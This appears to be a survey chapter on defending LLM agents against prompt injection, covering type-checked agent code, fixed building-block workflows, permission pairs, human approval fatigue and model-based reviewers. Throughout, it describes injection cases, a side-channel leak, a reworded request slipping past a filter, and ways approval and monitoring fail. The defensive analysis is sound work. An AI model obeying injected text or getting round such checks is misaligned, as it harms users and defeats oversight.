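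CaMeL trusts its planner and keeps untrusted text away from it, whereas TACIT lets its agent read untrusted text and treats the agent as a possible attacker. A malicious web page can still cause a TACIT agent to try something harmful, but the agent's code has to pass the compiler's check.

### What the TACIT experiments found

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT with two models, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and MiniMax M2.5, on a sample software project with a folder of access keys, a database and confidential documents. Each model did 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 planted attacks, for 120 trials per model. Each model also received 11 malicious requests. Some were direct requests for secrets, and others were written as if they came from someone such as a system administrator.

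When the secrets were in `Classified` containers, neither model's output contained a secret in any of its 131 trials. With plain-text secrets, Claude leaked them in two trials, both with malicious requests, and MiniMax leaked them in 11, three with planted attacks and eight with malicious requests. The containers didn't make the agents less useful. Claude completed 99.2% of the ordinary tasks with them and 83.3% without, though the researchers suspect the setup caused the difference, since Claude often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user.

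This test measures exactly what the compiler is meant to guarantee. A perfect score is good evidence that the guarantee works in practice, but not that the agent is safe in other ways. The test also shows how much, without the containers, depends on the model.

Two further tests measured whether writing typed Scala makes agents worse at their work. On τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer-service conversations, all three models tested scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with TACIT than with ordinary tool calls, in both the airline and the retail tasks. Fewer than 8% of the programs there needed another attempt because of compiler errors. On SWE-bench Lite, which contains 300 real software problems, MiniMax M2.5 solved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without.

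The language itself therefore seems to reduce task completion only a little, but strict rules on data can still reduce it a lot. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) describes a system in which agents also have to write programs that pass a type check before they run. Garby and colleagues report that the Haskell version of that system completed 15 of AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks without its data-flow policies and 8 with them. CaMeL completed 7 under the same conditions.

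### LACUNA and the variables in scope

In *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), a developer leaves a gap in a program and states what type of result should fill it. When the program reaches the gap, an agent writes the missing code. The compiler checks this code as if the developer had written it there, so it can use only the variables and functions that are in scope (visible at that point). These variables and functions are therefore the agent's permissions. If a file-reading function is in scope but nothing that uses the network is, the agent can read files but can't send their contents over the network.

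LACUNA's compiler accepts or rejects the agent's code as a whole. In one example, the agent should subtract 50 from a balance of 100 and return the new number. It writes code that subtracts the 50 but returns a sentence. In ordinary Python, the balance would already have changed by the time the mistake caused an error. LACUNA's compiler rejects the code for returning the wrong type before any of it runs, so the balance stays at 100.

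Capture checking also stops code from keeping a capability for later. Suppose the host gives a gap temporary access to the file system. The agent may read a file and return its text, but it may not return a function that reads files, because the function would keep the access. This matters for agent-made tools because a saved tool is a function that outlives the task it was made for, so the host would have to grant access each time the tool runs.

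Odersky, Zhao and their colleagues ran both systems on AgentDojo and compared them with CaMeL's published results. The percentages show how often each agent finished the user's task, and the last column counts successful attacks out of about 950:

| System and model | Banking | Workspace | Slack | Travel | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, o4-mini-high | 62.5% | 81.4% | 68.6% | 74.3% | 1 |
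| TACIT, o4-mini-high | 59.0% | 52.9% | 47.6% | 68.6% | 1 |
| LACUNA, o4-mini-high | 66.0% | 55.5% | 49.5% | 71.4% | 1 |
| CaMeL, Gemini 2.5 Pro | 52.8% | 53.8% | 48.6% | 1.4% | 0 |
| TACIT, Gemini 2.5 Pro | 56.9% | 50.5% | 40.0% | 64.3% | 0 |
| LACUNA, Gemini 2.5 Pro | 63.2% | 56.3% | 42.9% | 63.6% | 7 |

With o4-mini-high, CaMeL finished far more of the workspace and Slack tasks than TACIT. Odersky and colleagues call the two systems comparably useful, which is fair for banking. All three systems stopped nearly every attack. LACUNA's compiler permits any use of a capability the developer has put in scope, and Zhao and colleagues link the system's failures to this design limit. If a task legitimately requires sending messages, an attacker may be able to steer what the agent sends.

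LACUNA's results on τ²-bench are less encouraging than TACIT's. With DeepSeek-V4-Flash, LACUNA solved 76.0% of 392 tasks, while an agent with ordinary tool calls solved 90.0%. The paper describes these results as on par, which understates the 14-point gap. The two papers used different models and different ways of running the conversation, so it is unclear how much typed code lowers success rates in general.

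### What the guarantees depend on

All these guarantees assume that the program doing the checking is correct. CaMeL's interpreter dropped labels for reasons its developers hadn't noticed. TACIT uses an existing compiler, which many more people have tested, but its capture checking is still experimental. The compiler also has to forbid language features that get around types, such as reflection, which lets code look up functions by name while the program runs. Scala has a safe mode that forbids these features, and Zhao and colleagues say that without it a host must treat the agent's program as ordinary untrusted code.

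The policies also have to be right. If a policy mistakenly allows anyone in the company to receive customer records, CaMeL won't stop the records from going to an employee who shouldn't have them. In LACUNA, the equivalent mistake is leaving an email function in scope when the task doesn't need it.

Finally, these checks depend on correct wrappers, the functions that connect the checked program to real files and services. A wrapper that returns a secret as plain text instead of in a `Classified` container bypasses TACIT's protection, and the compiler can't detect that the text was secret. TACIT also lets programmers mark a library as safe without a check, which is sometimes necessary, but the programmer then has to make sure the library is safe. In CaMeL, a tool that labels a stranger's email as trusted likewise bypasses the protection. People therefore need to review these functions, and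 an agent shouldn't be able to write or change them.

The check also ends when a TACIT program starts another program, because the compiler can't follow the data into it. Odersky and colleagues recommend allowing only a short list of commands and using a sandbox underneath. The sandbox also helps if a flaw in the compiler or interpreter lets code escape.

Analyzing a tool's code can miss a leak that passes through the model. *PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes a mail skill whose code sends whatever text the model gives it. The harmless version comes with instructions to fill in a template, and the malicious version comes with instructions to copy a password from the model's context. Both versions have the same code, so no analysis of the code alone can tell them apart. The difference first appears when the model makes the call, so the paper's system checks every call just before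 it runs. TACIT instead keeps classified data out of the main agent's context, but that doesn't help with a password the agent has already read somewhere else.

### Wrong but permitted actions

The two attacks that succeeded against Garby and colleagues' agent were runs of the same case. The user asked the agent to read a text file and make the payment it described, but the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. The agent followed the user's instructions and so made the attacker's payment. A rule against using the file's contents would have blocked the attack, but also every legitimate payment of that kind.

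TACIT's one failure on AgentDojo was a milder case. The user wanted to book a hotel, and the attacker had planted a recommendation for another hotel in the reviews. The agent booked the right one but quoted the reviews in its answer, and the benchmark counted the mention of the other hotel as a successful attack. The rules rightly allowed public reviews to reach the user.

Data-flow rules don't check whether a calculation is correct, either. An agent can pass every check and still return a wrong total or cancel the wrong order. Most of these systems also ignore side channels, which carry information through something other than the data itself. One of Tallam and Miller's examples is a loop that reads a secret number and requests a web page that many times. Each request is harmless, but anyone who can read the website's log can learn the number by counting them. TACIT's developers also exclude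 timing leaks, such as a function that takes longer when a certain digit in a secret is high.

### The expense tool with data-flow rules

With host functions alone, the expense tool could put the text of a private receipt in the description column of the team's spreadsheet. A data-flow rule can prevent this. The obvious rule is that only the worker may read anything from a receipt, but then the tool couldn't do its job, because the date, total and currency also come from receipts. The worker needs a rule with exceptions:

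| Data from a receipt | Exchange-rate service | Team spreadsheet | Any other address |
|---|---|---|---|
| Date and currency | Yes | Yes | No |
| Total | No | Yes | No |
| Category from a fixed list | No | Yes | No |
| Any other text | No | No | No |

In CaMeL, a developer would write this as policies for the functions that fetch a rate and add a row. In TACIT, the receipts would arrive in `Classified` containers, and the agent's code could extract a total but couldn't take it out of the container. A developer would have to write a function that accepts a classified row, checks that it contains only a date, an amount, a currency and a category, and adds it to the spreadsheet. The privacy of the receipts then depends on that function. If it also accepted a free-text description, the code would still compile, but receipt data could leak through the description.

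The stranger's instruction now has little effect. CaMeL's planner writes its program without reading any receipts, so the instruction can't make it add an upload. But the planner also can't check how sample receipts are laid out, so it has to rely on the reader to find the date and total. A TACIT agent that tries to read a sample sees only `Classified(****)`, so it would use the trusted model to extract the fields.

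When hotels start emailing their receipts, someone still has to give the tool a function for the mailbox. But the rules about where receipt data may go can stay the same, as long as the new function labels attachments the same way as files in the receipts folder. It's safest for the host to give the strictest label to data from any source that nobody has classified yet. A mistake then stops the tool, which the worker will notice, rather than exposing the mailbox.

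The rules don't help if the stranger's receipt lists a €90 hotel room at €900, because they allow amounts from receipts to go into the team's spreadsheet.

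## What is gained and lost when an agent may only combine fixed building blocks?

In the fifth design, the agent picks building blocks from a list and connects the output of one to the input of another, without writing any code of its own. The result is a graph or a short declarative program, which is a list of steps that the host's own engine carries out. Even a calculation such as currency conversion is a block that a developer has written and tested.

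*A Declarative Language for Building And Orchestrating LLM-Powered Agent Workflows* (2025) contrasts this style with frameworks that put an agent's logic in application code, where developers may have to update and redeploy a service to change the agent. *SPL* (2026) describes a related approach called Compiled AI, in which a language model writes a fixed program once and is not called when the program runs. A tool made of blocks can work the same way, unless one of its blocks calls a model.

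### The expense tool without free code

An agent could submit the expense tool in this form:

```
for each new file in the receipts folder:
    receipt  = read_receipt(file)
    fields   = extract_fields(receipt)
    rate     = get_rate(fields.date, fields.currency)
    euros    = convert(fields.total, rate)
    decision = ask_worker(fields, euros)
    when decision is "approved":
        add_row(fields.date, euros, fields.category)
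    otherwise: stop
```

Each block declares the types of its inputs and outputs. `add_row` takes a date, an amount in euros and a category from a fixed list, so the agent can't pass it the receipt's text or an amount in dollars. The host checks that connected blocks have matching types when the agent submits the tool. It also has to check the values during each run, because `extract_fields` may use a language model, which could return "about 90" for a total. *Small Language Models for Agentic Systems* (Sharma and Mehta, 2025) recommends this kind of check, which compares a call's inputs with a formal description of the permitted values before the call runs.

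A checker can answer three questions about this tool before it handles a single receipt:

- It reads from the receipts folder and the exchange-rate service.
- It writes to the spreadsheet. It also sends a date and a currency to the exchange-rate service.
- The worker's approval lies on every path to the spreadsheet. To test this, the checker removes `ask_worker` from the graph and searches from the start. If the search still reaches `add_row`, there is a way around the approval.

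No checker can answer such questions for every program in an ordinary language, because code can build an address or choose a function while it runs. A simple search can answer them for a fixed graph of known blocks.

The types don't catch every mistake. If the agent connects today's date to `get_rate` instead of the receipt's date, the tool passes the check but uses the wrong rate. And only the worker can stop a receipt with an inflated total.

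### Six patterns for limiting an injection

*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) describes six ways to restrict an agent so that an injection can do little. In all six, once an agent has taken in untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger an action with harmful side effects.

| Pattern | How it works | What an injection can still do |
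|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from ready-made actions and never sees their results | Nothing through the data, since the model doesn't read it |
| Plan, then execute | The model lists its tool calls before it reads any data | Change what goes into a call, such as the text of an email |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and returns a restricted answer, such as yes or no | Falsify the answer for its own document |
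| Dual LLM | One model has the tools, and another reads untrusted text and passes it on as a sealed variable | Tamper with the text in the variable |
| Code, then execute | The model writes a whole program before any data arrives | Change what goes into a call |
| Context minimization | The host removes the user's prompt before the model writes its answer | Affect the step before the removal, such as a database query |

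CaMeL, which labels data as a program runs, is an example of the fifth pattern. The expense tool mostly follows the second, because its steps are fixed before any receipt arrives. Its `extract_fields` block resembles the map step in the third, because it reads one receipt and returns four restricted values. A malicious receipt can therefore falsify its own total, but it can't add an upload or change another receipt's row.

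This protection works only if the host hides the text of receipts from the agent until the graph is finished. Otherwise, safety depends on the check of the finished graph.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues apply the patterns to ten cases, and most of the stricter versions make the agent less useful. An agent that answers questions from a database can no longer read the results to check whether they answer the question. In the safest version of a programming agent, the agent sees only a formal description of outside code, with names limited to perhaps 30 characters and no examples or explanations.

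### What Agentproof checks

*Agentproof* (Xavier, Jolly and colleagues, 2026) presents a checker for graphs like these. The checker converts workflows from four popular frameworks for building agents to a common form, in which every step has a kind, such as a tool, a model call, a branch or a human decision. It then runs six checks for structural errors, such as steps that lead nowhere. When a check fails, it prints a path that shows the problem.

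The researchers tried it on 18 workflows that they had written themselves, based on the frameworks' own examples and on known mistakes. It found these defects:

| Defect | Number found | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Dead end | 2 | A step drafts an email, but nothing connects it to the step that sends it |
| Exit that no path reaches | 1 | Agents take turns brainstorming forever |
| Branch without conditions | 1 | A debate moderator passes the turn on unconditionally |
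| Tool step that names no tool | 1 | A data cleaner has an empty tool list |
| No human step anywhere | 10 | A workflow brings in a new employee or customer without approval |

The researchers built defects into the set, so the counts show what the checker can find but don't measure how common the defects are. The last row is also partly a matter of opinion. Xavier and colleagues call one of the ten a false alarm and others arguable, since a low-risk workflow may not need a person.

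The structural checks are fast enough that a host could run them every time an agent proposes a tool. They took about 105 milliseconds on an artificial graph of 5,000 steps, and the 18 workflows had between 5 and 12 steps each. Searching the graph also covers paths that a test may never take. In one workflow, ten random runs missed a path on which a draft email got no human review, but the search found it.

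A host must choose its approval check carefully. The basic check passes any workflow that contains a human step, even if that step is on a different branch from the payment. An optional check tests every path to a sensitive tool by removing the human steps, as in the expense example. Agentproof also has a small language for rules about the order of steps. One of the paper's sample rules requires an approval to follow when a workflow deploys software (puts it into live use), so a workflow can satisfy the rule as written by deploying first and asking for approval afterward.

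With the LangGraph framework, Agentproof identifies a human step by the word "human" in its name, so it misses an approval step called "manager sign-off". A host with fixed blocks avoids this problem because its developers know which block requires human input. Agentproof also treats every branch as possible, so it can report paths that no real run would take. Its results no longer hold if the graph changes during a run.

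### How safe blocks make an unsafe tool

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe an assistant that sorts a user's files. Before it reads anything, it commits to using only two commands, `find`, which searches for files, and `mv`, which moves them. An injected instruction can still cause it to find sensitive files and move them to a public network drive. The task needs both commands, and neither is dangerous enough to forbid.

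The number of such combinations grows faster than the number of blocks. Suppose a host offers 12 blocks that each read one source and 5 that each write to one destination. Someone grants 17 permissions, one per block, but the agent can connect any source to any destination:

12 × 5 = 60 pairs

A sixth writing block adds one permission but 12 more pairs. Pairs multiply the same way in a shared sandbox, which makes it risky, but here the host can see which pairs a tool uses. An expense tool that reads receipts and exchange rates and writes to one spreadsheet uses three pairs: receipts to spreadsheet, exchange rates to spreadsheet, and receipts to the exchange-rate service. A person can review a table of 60 pairs once and mark the forbidden ones. The checker then compares every new tool with that table.

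To find a tool's pairs, the checker follows the connections from each source and treats everything they lead to as containing that source's data. *Data Leakage Prevention in Agentic Applications via Preemptive Hardening* (2026) applies a similar method to the source code of agent applications, marking the tools that send data out and then carrying sensitivity labels along each path toward them. A graph of blocks is easier to analyze than source code because every connection is explicit, but following connections is less precise than tracking individual values.

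The table of pairs has two gaps. The first is that tools can be chained. Suppose the rules forbid sending receipts by email, but one tool copies receipt data to the spreadsheet and another emails the spreadsheet to a client. Each tool uses only permitted pairs, but together they produce the forbidden pair. The checker therefore has to examine saved tools together whenever one reads what another writes. *Securing Multi-Tool AI Agent Chains With Dynamic, Real-Time Compositional Policies* (2026) describes the general problem, which is that a sequence of properly authorized calls can have more combined access than any single policy was meant to grant.

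The second gap is that harmless data can become sensitive when combined. *Agent Tools Orchestration Leaks More* (2025) studies this with ordinary tools and no attacker. While doing a harmless task, an agent combines observations that reveal nothing separately and infers something private about the user. Train receipts and a calendar, for example, might together show that someone visits a hospital every Tuesday. Twelve sources form 4,095 possible groups, and pairing each group with one of five destinations gives 20,475 combinations, which nobody will review one by one. It's more practical to limit how many sources a single tool may read and have a person review any tool that needs more.

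### Offering only the blocks a task needs

The host can also reduce the number of combinations by showing the agent fewer blocks. If a task needs two reading blocks and one writing block, the agent gets three permissions and can make only two read-write pairs, however many other blocks the host has.

Zhu and Wang (2026), in *Intent-Governed Tool Authorization for AI Agents*, derive the list from the user's request. Their host turns the request into a short-lived certificate that states the kinds of action the request justifies and their limits. The host hides the tools that don't fit, then checks each proposed call against the certificate. For example, a request to summarize this month's records justifies reading records but not exporting them in bulk. The certificate can only narrow the permissions the agent already has.

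In a small synthetic test with 7 tools and 12 tasks, a fixed tool list showed the agent a high-risk tool without justification from the task 33 times. Narrowing the list to hide such tools eliminated these cases, but the agent could still misuse a tool it legitimately had, for instance by entering an amount of 2,350 when the user had said 23.50. With narrowing alone, 2 of the 7 hostile or ambiguous tasks still ended in an unsafe action. Checking the inputs of each call prevented all unsafe actions, even with the full list visible.

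Results were much worse when language models wrote the certificates and proposed the calls. Zhu and Wang ran three open-weight models through 198 hostile or ambiguous trials. The host accepted 40 unsafe drafts but executed none. In 24 of the 40, the request was inflated in this way and the certificate's limits were missing or too weak. The models usually recognized what kind of action the user wanted but often missed the exact record or amount.

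None of the 108 harmless trials finished without review. A third produced a draft for a person to approve, and most of the rest failed because the model wrote a malformed call. Stronger models should make fewer such errors, but until one reliably avoids them, a developer or the user should set the limits that matter most.

*Capability Minimization as a Safety Primitive* (Iyer and Suresh Babu, 2026) narrows the list again at every step. The host shows the agent a risky tool only if the tool is on the best-scoring path to the goal, with risk counting against a path, and a trusted step has already authorized it. For example, an email agent isn't shown `send_email` until the recipient is confirmed. On a synthetic benchmark with 100 tools, this reduced the average number of risky tools visible per step from 26 to 0.18. Although the test agent obeyed every injected instruction it could, the share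 of successful attacks fell from 100% to zero.

That zero follows almost directly from the design, since an agent can't call a tool the host has withheld. The agent still completed every task, which is the more informative result. Seven real language models also made no risky calls under attack with this method, compared with 25% for a filter based on usefulness but not risk.

The protection fails if an attacker can forge the authorization, for instance if the text of an email can mark a recipient as confirmed. The benchmark's standard for authorization is lenient, since reading an email counts as approval to delete it. Iyer and Suresh Babu also note that their risk labels apply to single tools and miss the danger of combining them. A host that narrows the list therefore still needs the table of pairs.

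### When no block fits

When hotels start emailing their receipts, the agent can't extend the expense tool until a developer writes and reviews a block that reads the mailbox. If the new block returns the same type as `read_receipt`, the agent can replace `read_receipt` with it without changing the other steps. Someone must also decide whether the new block may be paired with each of the five writing blocks.

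Beurer-Kellner and colleagues find the same drawback in their file assistant. A fixed set of commands makes it immune to injected text, but developers have to do most of the work in advance, and the assistant mostly loses its ability to search by meaning. In their customer-service example, the system also blocks reasonable requests that are unlike any the developers anticipated.

Where people already know the procedure, fixed steps can improve the results. In *Blueprint First, Model Second*, Qiu, Ye and colleagues (2025) had experts write a workflow as ordinary code that calls a language model only for limited jobs. On TravelPlanner, a test of planning trips under many constraints, this system produced an acceptable plan in 35.56% of cases and broke the constraints 11 times, compared with 18.00% and 275 times for the best earlier system using the same model. Rules such as "never repeat a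 restaurant" are written into the code, so enforcing them doesn't depend on the model. But people designed that workflow for trip planning, so the result is little evidence of how well an agent would choose the steps itself.

Qiu and colleagues also reduce the work of writing workflows. Users describe what they want, a model drafts a template, and users refine it. Developers can combine several calls into one larger block, which in a retail example cut the number of tool calls from 11 to 2. Larger blocks also improve security. If one block reads a receipt and adds its row, and the agent can't use the two steps separately, the agent can't send the receipt anywhere else.

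### Broad blocks and approval for new tools

If a new block takes a week to arrive, users will look for a way around the wait, and block systems often include one. n8n, a platform for building automated workflows from connected blocks, has a block that sends a request to any web address and another that runs code. *Characterizing Large Language Model Agentic Workflows* (Tang, Zhou and Chen, 2026) lists both among n8n's standard parts. With the web block, an agent can fetch receipts from a new source immediately, but it can also send them anywhere. The code block lets the agent write free-form code again, which runs with whatever access the host gives it. A checker can still report that a tool contains such a block, but not which data the block will read or where it will send that data.

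A host can make the web block safer by requiring the address to be a constant in the graph. The checker can then treat each address as a separate destination, and a person can approve the exchange-rate service without approving the rest of the internet. A code block needs a sandbox with no network access and no files beyond its inputs. A shell runs any command and has no such simple fix, so it doesn't belong on the list.

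The strictest policy forbids an agent from creating a tool during a task without someone's approval. There is a good case for this, because no one has reviewed a new tool, and Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think it unlikely that general-purpose agents built on current language models can give reliable safety guarantees. In practice, however, if every small rearrangement of blocks needs approval, people will approve requests without reading them or ask for one broad block that makes further requests unnecessary.

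The table of pairs is a better basis for deciding which tools need review. A tool that uses only permitted pairs, and has an approval step before any payment or deletion, can run without a separate review. A person must review any tool that needs a new pair, block or address before it runs. This leaves some risk from chains of tools and from sensitive combinations, but people review fewer tools and have a specific question to answer about each. The host should also record which blocks agents request but don't find, so that developers can write the most useful ones before users turn to a broad substitute.

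### Approval steps in 6,003 workflows

Approval is optional on most block platforms, and people rarely include it. Tang, Zhou and Chen examined 6,003 public n8n workflows that use a language model. Starting from each model step, they followed the graph for up to six steps to see whether the output could reach an outside action, such as sending an email or changing a database, and what lay in between:

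| Between the model and the action | Workflows | Share |
|---|---|---|
| A human decision | 167 | 2.78% |
| Workflow logic, such as a condition or a parser | 2,509 | 41.80% |
| Neither | 1,592 | 26.52% |
| No path to an outside action | 1,363 | 22.71% |
| No traceable model step | 372 | 6.20% |

Even among the 4,268 workflows whose model output could reach an outside action, only 3.9% had a human decision on the way. This figure overstates human control in one respect, because it includes workflows that also have a path without approval. It may also omit approval steps with unusual names. The second row is weak evidence of protection, since it includes steps that only format the model's output.

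These are public templates, many of them probably examples or tutorials, and their users may add approval before relying on them. The study also covers how people designed the workflows, not what happened when the workflows ran. It is still good evidence that people won't necessarily use an approval block just because one is available, so a host that depends on approval should require it and check for it in the graph.

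One of the workflows resembles the expense tool. A user uploads an invoice, the workflow extracts the text, and a Claude model picks out the vendor and the amounts. Further steps repair the format, look for duplicates and compare the invoice with existing records. Ambiguous cases go to a person, who marks the invoice as paid or unpaid or archives it. But no step compares the extracted amounts with the original invoice. If the model reads €90 as €900 and the record otherwise looks normal, the workflow does not send the invoice to a person for review.

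## How much protection does approval add?

Sending every record in the invoice workflow to a reviewer would help only if the reviewer could see that an amount was wrong and was still paying attention. What the reviewer can see depends on what the host presents for approval.

### Four things to approve

A host can ask someone to approve a tool's source code. A worker who can program would probably notice if the stranger's receipt had led the agent to add an upload to the expense tool, and might notice that the tool uses today's exchange rate for old receipts. But the worker is unlikely to read the libraries the tool imports, and some flaws look like good code, as the `extractall` call in the tar tool did.

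A list of permissions is easier to read than code. An expense tool's list might allow it to open the receipts folder, contact the exchange-rate service and add rows to the team's spreadsheet. Someone who can't program can understand that list, and can ask why an expense tool needs access to the whole mailbox. The list also limits what the code can do, even if nobody has read it. But it doesn't show what the tool does within those limits, such as converting at the wrong rate or copying private text into a description.

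The host can instead request approval for one action with its actual arguments, such as adding a row for a hotel at €900 on November 3. The worker can reject an impossible date or an unknown recipient, but the request doesn't show that the receipt was for €90. A request to run `python expenses.py` shows even less. The command may also set off actions that the approval doesn't cover. A software practitioner interviewed for *Let the Agent Do It?* (Salerno, Gao and colleagues, 2026) had approved an action, but the agent did something other than what the practitioner expected.

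Finally, the host can preview the effect. It could run the expense tool on a copy of the spreadsheet, then show the new row beside the receipt and highlight any other cells that changed. The worker can now catch both the €900 and a tool that overwrites a colleague's rows. The preview can't show that the receipt is false, or what an outside service will do with the data it receives. It also goes out of date if someone edits the real spreadsheet before the worker approves. And a developer has to build a preview for each kind of action.

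### How carefully people review code and set rules

Reviewers seem to get less demanding with agent-written code as they see more of it. *Habituation at the Gate* (Yu, Jia and colleagues, 2026) followed 400 people who repeatedly reviewed pull requests (proposed code changes) from agents on GitHub in 2025. The approval rate rose from 30.1% in the first half of each person's reviews to 36.8% in the second. Comments on specific lines fell by 22% between their earliest tenth of reviews and their latest. Approval of human-written changes in the same projects fell over the period, so the reviewers hadn't simply become more lenient with all code. But the agents' code may have improved, and the study didn't measure its quality.

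*Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) tested rules that people set in advance. 113 people from outside the software industry supervised a simulated assistant through 18 actions, seven of which went beyond the assigned task. One group decided on every action. A second decided only on those a model passed to them. The third first chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for spending money, sending information, deleting things and reading private data.

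The group with rules did worst, blocking about 40% of the overreaching actions, compared with 60% for people who decided on everything and 54% for those helped by a model. They had chosen "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, which put off the decision, and then approved 67% of the overreaching actions they were asked about. Some of these actions were mild, such as calling the airport to confirm a flight, and people may have wanted them. Still, the 16 "never" rules blocked 31 actions without needing anyone's attention again. A permission list protects people in the same way only if it decides in advance whether an action is allowed.

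### Approval fatigue

People who review generated code carefully don't necessarily review an agent's actions carefully. *From Delegation to Action Approval* (Wu, Wermke et al., 2026) surveyed 203 users of coding agents. Of the 105 who said they carefully reviewed most or all generated code, 61% said they often approved at least one kind of action without close review. The figure for the others was 67%, but the difference was not statistically significant. The share who often approved an action without close review was highest for access to the internet and connected tools, at 36%, and lowest for reading secrets, at 21%.

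Knowing about the risks didn't seem to make people more careful. Of those aware of a security incident or a worrying practice involving agents, 70% often approved something without reviewing it closely, compared with 43% of those who weren't.

All of this evidence is self-reported. People misremember, and some give the answer that makes them look careful. Salerno and colleagues also relied on self-report when they surveyed practitioners, of whom 47.7% said they read permission requests carefully and 20.6% said they approved by default. Quick approval can also be sensible when an action is familiar and low-risk.

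Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that Claude Code users accept 93% of permission prompts, and Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports 97%. These rates don't prove that users are careless, because if 1 request in 500 were harmful, a perfect reviewer would still approve 99.8% of them.

Measuring reviewers' attention requires planting a bad request. Anthropic tested 1,053 paid testers by replacing one prompt in each session with a clearly dangerous command that would never run. The testers rejected 13.6% of these commands overall, about 17% early in a session but only about 5% after 50 or more prompts. This is the best evidence of fatigue so far, though the testers weren't working on their own projects and had less to lose than real users, and Anthropic published the result to explain why it was replacing manual prompts. A company can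 run the same test on its own staff. *Agent Reliability Profiles in Financial Services* (2026) recommends planting wrong but harmless proposals, which the host stops before they take effect, and recording how long reviewers take and how often they edit or reject.

Many users turn off approval prompts. Resilient Cyber's *The Human in the Loop Illusion* reports on an Anthropic study in which new users approved everything automatically in about 20% of sessions, rising to over 40% by their 750th session. Other users write a rule that lets every command starting with `python` run without approval. Anthropic found many such rules, and OpenAI found them among its own staff. For agent-made tools, such a rule is almost the same as having no approval, because it covers every Python tool the agent writes.

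### Fewer and better-chosen requests

As an illustration with made-up numbers, suppose an agent makes 10,000 requests a year, 1 in 500 is harmful, and the reviewer catches 80% of the harmful ones:

10,000 ÷ 500 = 20 harmful requests

20 × 20% = 4 that the reviewer lets through

Now suppose a sandbox and fixed rules settle 9,500 routine requests, so that only 500 reach the reviewer. Someone who spent 10 seconds on each of 10,000 requests could spend 200 seconds on each of 500 in the same total time. If that raises the share they catch to 95%, the result depends on whether the harmful requests are among the 500:

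| Requests shown | Harmful ones among them | Share caught | Harmful actions that run |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10,000 | 20 | 80% | 4 |
| 10,000 | 20 | 13.6%, as in Anthropic's test | 17 |
| 500 | 20 | 95% | 1 |
| 500 | 18, because the rules let 2 run unasked | 95% | 3 |

If the rules let four harmful actions run without approval, the total rises to about five, and asking about everything at 80% would have been better.

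People also may not look harder when they get fewer requests. In Yan's experiment, the group helped by a model got 10 requests instead of 18, and seven of the 10 were overreaching. That group approved 46% of those seven, slightly more than the 40% approved by people who were asked about everything. A session of 18 actions is too short to cause much fatigue, so the experiment doesn't show what happens over a year. But Anthropic's testers missed most dangerous commands even when they were fresh, so cutting the number of prompts can't be enough.

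The information in an approval request probably matters too. Wu and colleagues found that developers who inspect diffs, which show each changed line, were less likely to approve four risky kinds of action without close review. They leave the hypothesis that previews cause better decisions for future studies. Anthropic's users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents but only 3% of single requests. They seem to at least read the plans, though they can reject them for reasons unrelated to safety.

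### Pausing when the code contains a sensitive call

Approval gives no protection if the program that runs is different from the one the person had in mind. One remedy is to ask for approval after the agent has written its code. *Governance by Construction for Generalist Agents* (Shlomov, Shoham and colleagues, 2026) describes how IBM's agent CUGA does this. An administrator lists the sensitive tools. After generating a program, CUGA scans it for calls to those tools and, if it finds one, pauses until someone approves. Administrators can also configure automatic approval, in which case no person is asked.

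In the demonstration, a user asks to delete every contact in a customer database, and a request filter blocks it. A reworded request gets past the filter and the agent writes code to delete a database, but the scan finds the deletion call and pauses. The scan is harder to fool with rewording because it checks the code rather than the request.

If the list included the function that adds rows, the scan would stop the expense tool before it added any rows. But the call may be in a loop that adds one row or 300, and the amounts don't exist until the program runs. A scan for names could also miss a function that the code chooses while it runs. A host that pauses each call as it arrives has the real arguments, but it may stop a program halfway through.

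CUGA's published results don't show how many harmful calls the approval pause catches. On 26 back-office tasks, the whole policy system raised one open-weight model's success rate from 49.2% to 82.3%. That gain doesn't measure the protection approval adds, because much of the system gives the agent better instructions and the benchmark counts finished tasks.

### Guarded Commits

Before agents, the person who approved a code change usually also held the login that carried it out. An agent may hold that login while a person approves in another program, so the action can go ahead without the approval. Bindschaedler, Kossmann and colleagues (2026), in *Guarded Commits*, give the login only to an adapter, a small trusted program that checks the approval immediately before an irreversible action. With the expense tool, it could work like this:

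1. The host fixes the version of the policy and the plan of steps. Every path to the spreadsheet includes an approval.
2. The tool prepares its rows, and the worker reviews them beside the receipts.
3. The host records the decision in a ledger that allows additions but no changes. The entry includes the evidence the worker saw, the policy version and a hash of the rows. A hash is a short fingerprint that changes if the data does.
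4. The adapter checks that the steps the run actually took included the right approval, that the decision was made under the fixed policy, and that the rows still match the hash. If the host is reusing an earlier decision, the adapter also checks that the two cases match and that the reviewer still has the authority.
5. If everything matches, the adapter adds the rows.

If the agent changes €90 to €900 after the worker approves, the hash no longer matches and the adapter rejects the request. An ordinary log might record only that the worker approved something that afternoon.

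Bindschaedler and colleagues tested the plan checker on 999 artificial plans, and it was correct on all of them. They also replayed 271,035 past decisions about code, translations and writing suggestions. Reusing a decision only when the case matched exactly would have avoided 0.9% of code reviews and 16.8% of translation reviews. They then added a rule that skipped review for short, supposedly low-risk translations. In roughly 63% of the extra cases it skipped, the outcome differed from the human's decision. This is a good reason to be wary of approving whole categories of action because they look safe.

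Nobody has yet compared the design with an approval system in daily use. The design also fails if the agent can find the login somewhere else. The researchers write that in Claude Code and the code editor Cursor, the terminal can typically access the user's own credentials. If a worker clicks "approve" without reading, the resulting record is as valid as any other.

### Models as reviewers

A model can review requests without getting tired. In Claude Code's auto mode, the host lets the agent read files and edit the project without review. A separate language model, the classifier, reviews most other actions, including shell commands. It first makes a quick decision that leans toward blocking, then reasons at more length about anything it flagged. The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls but not the tool results or the agent's explanations, so that neither a malicious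 receipt nor the agent's arguments can influence its decision. A separate check scans tool results for injected instructions.

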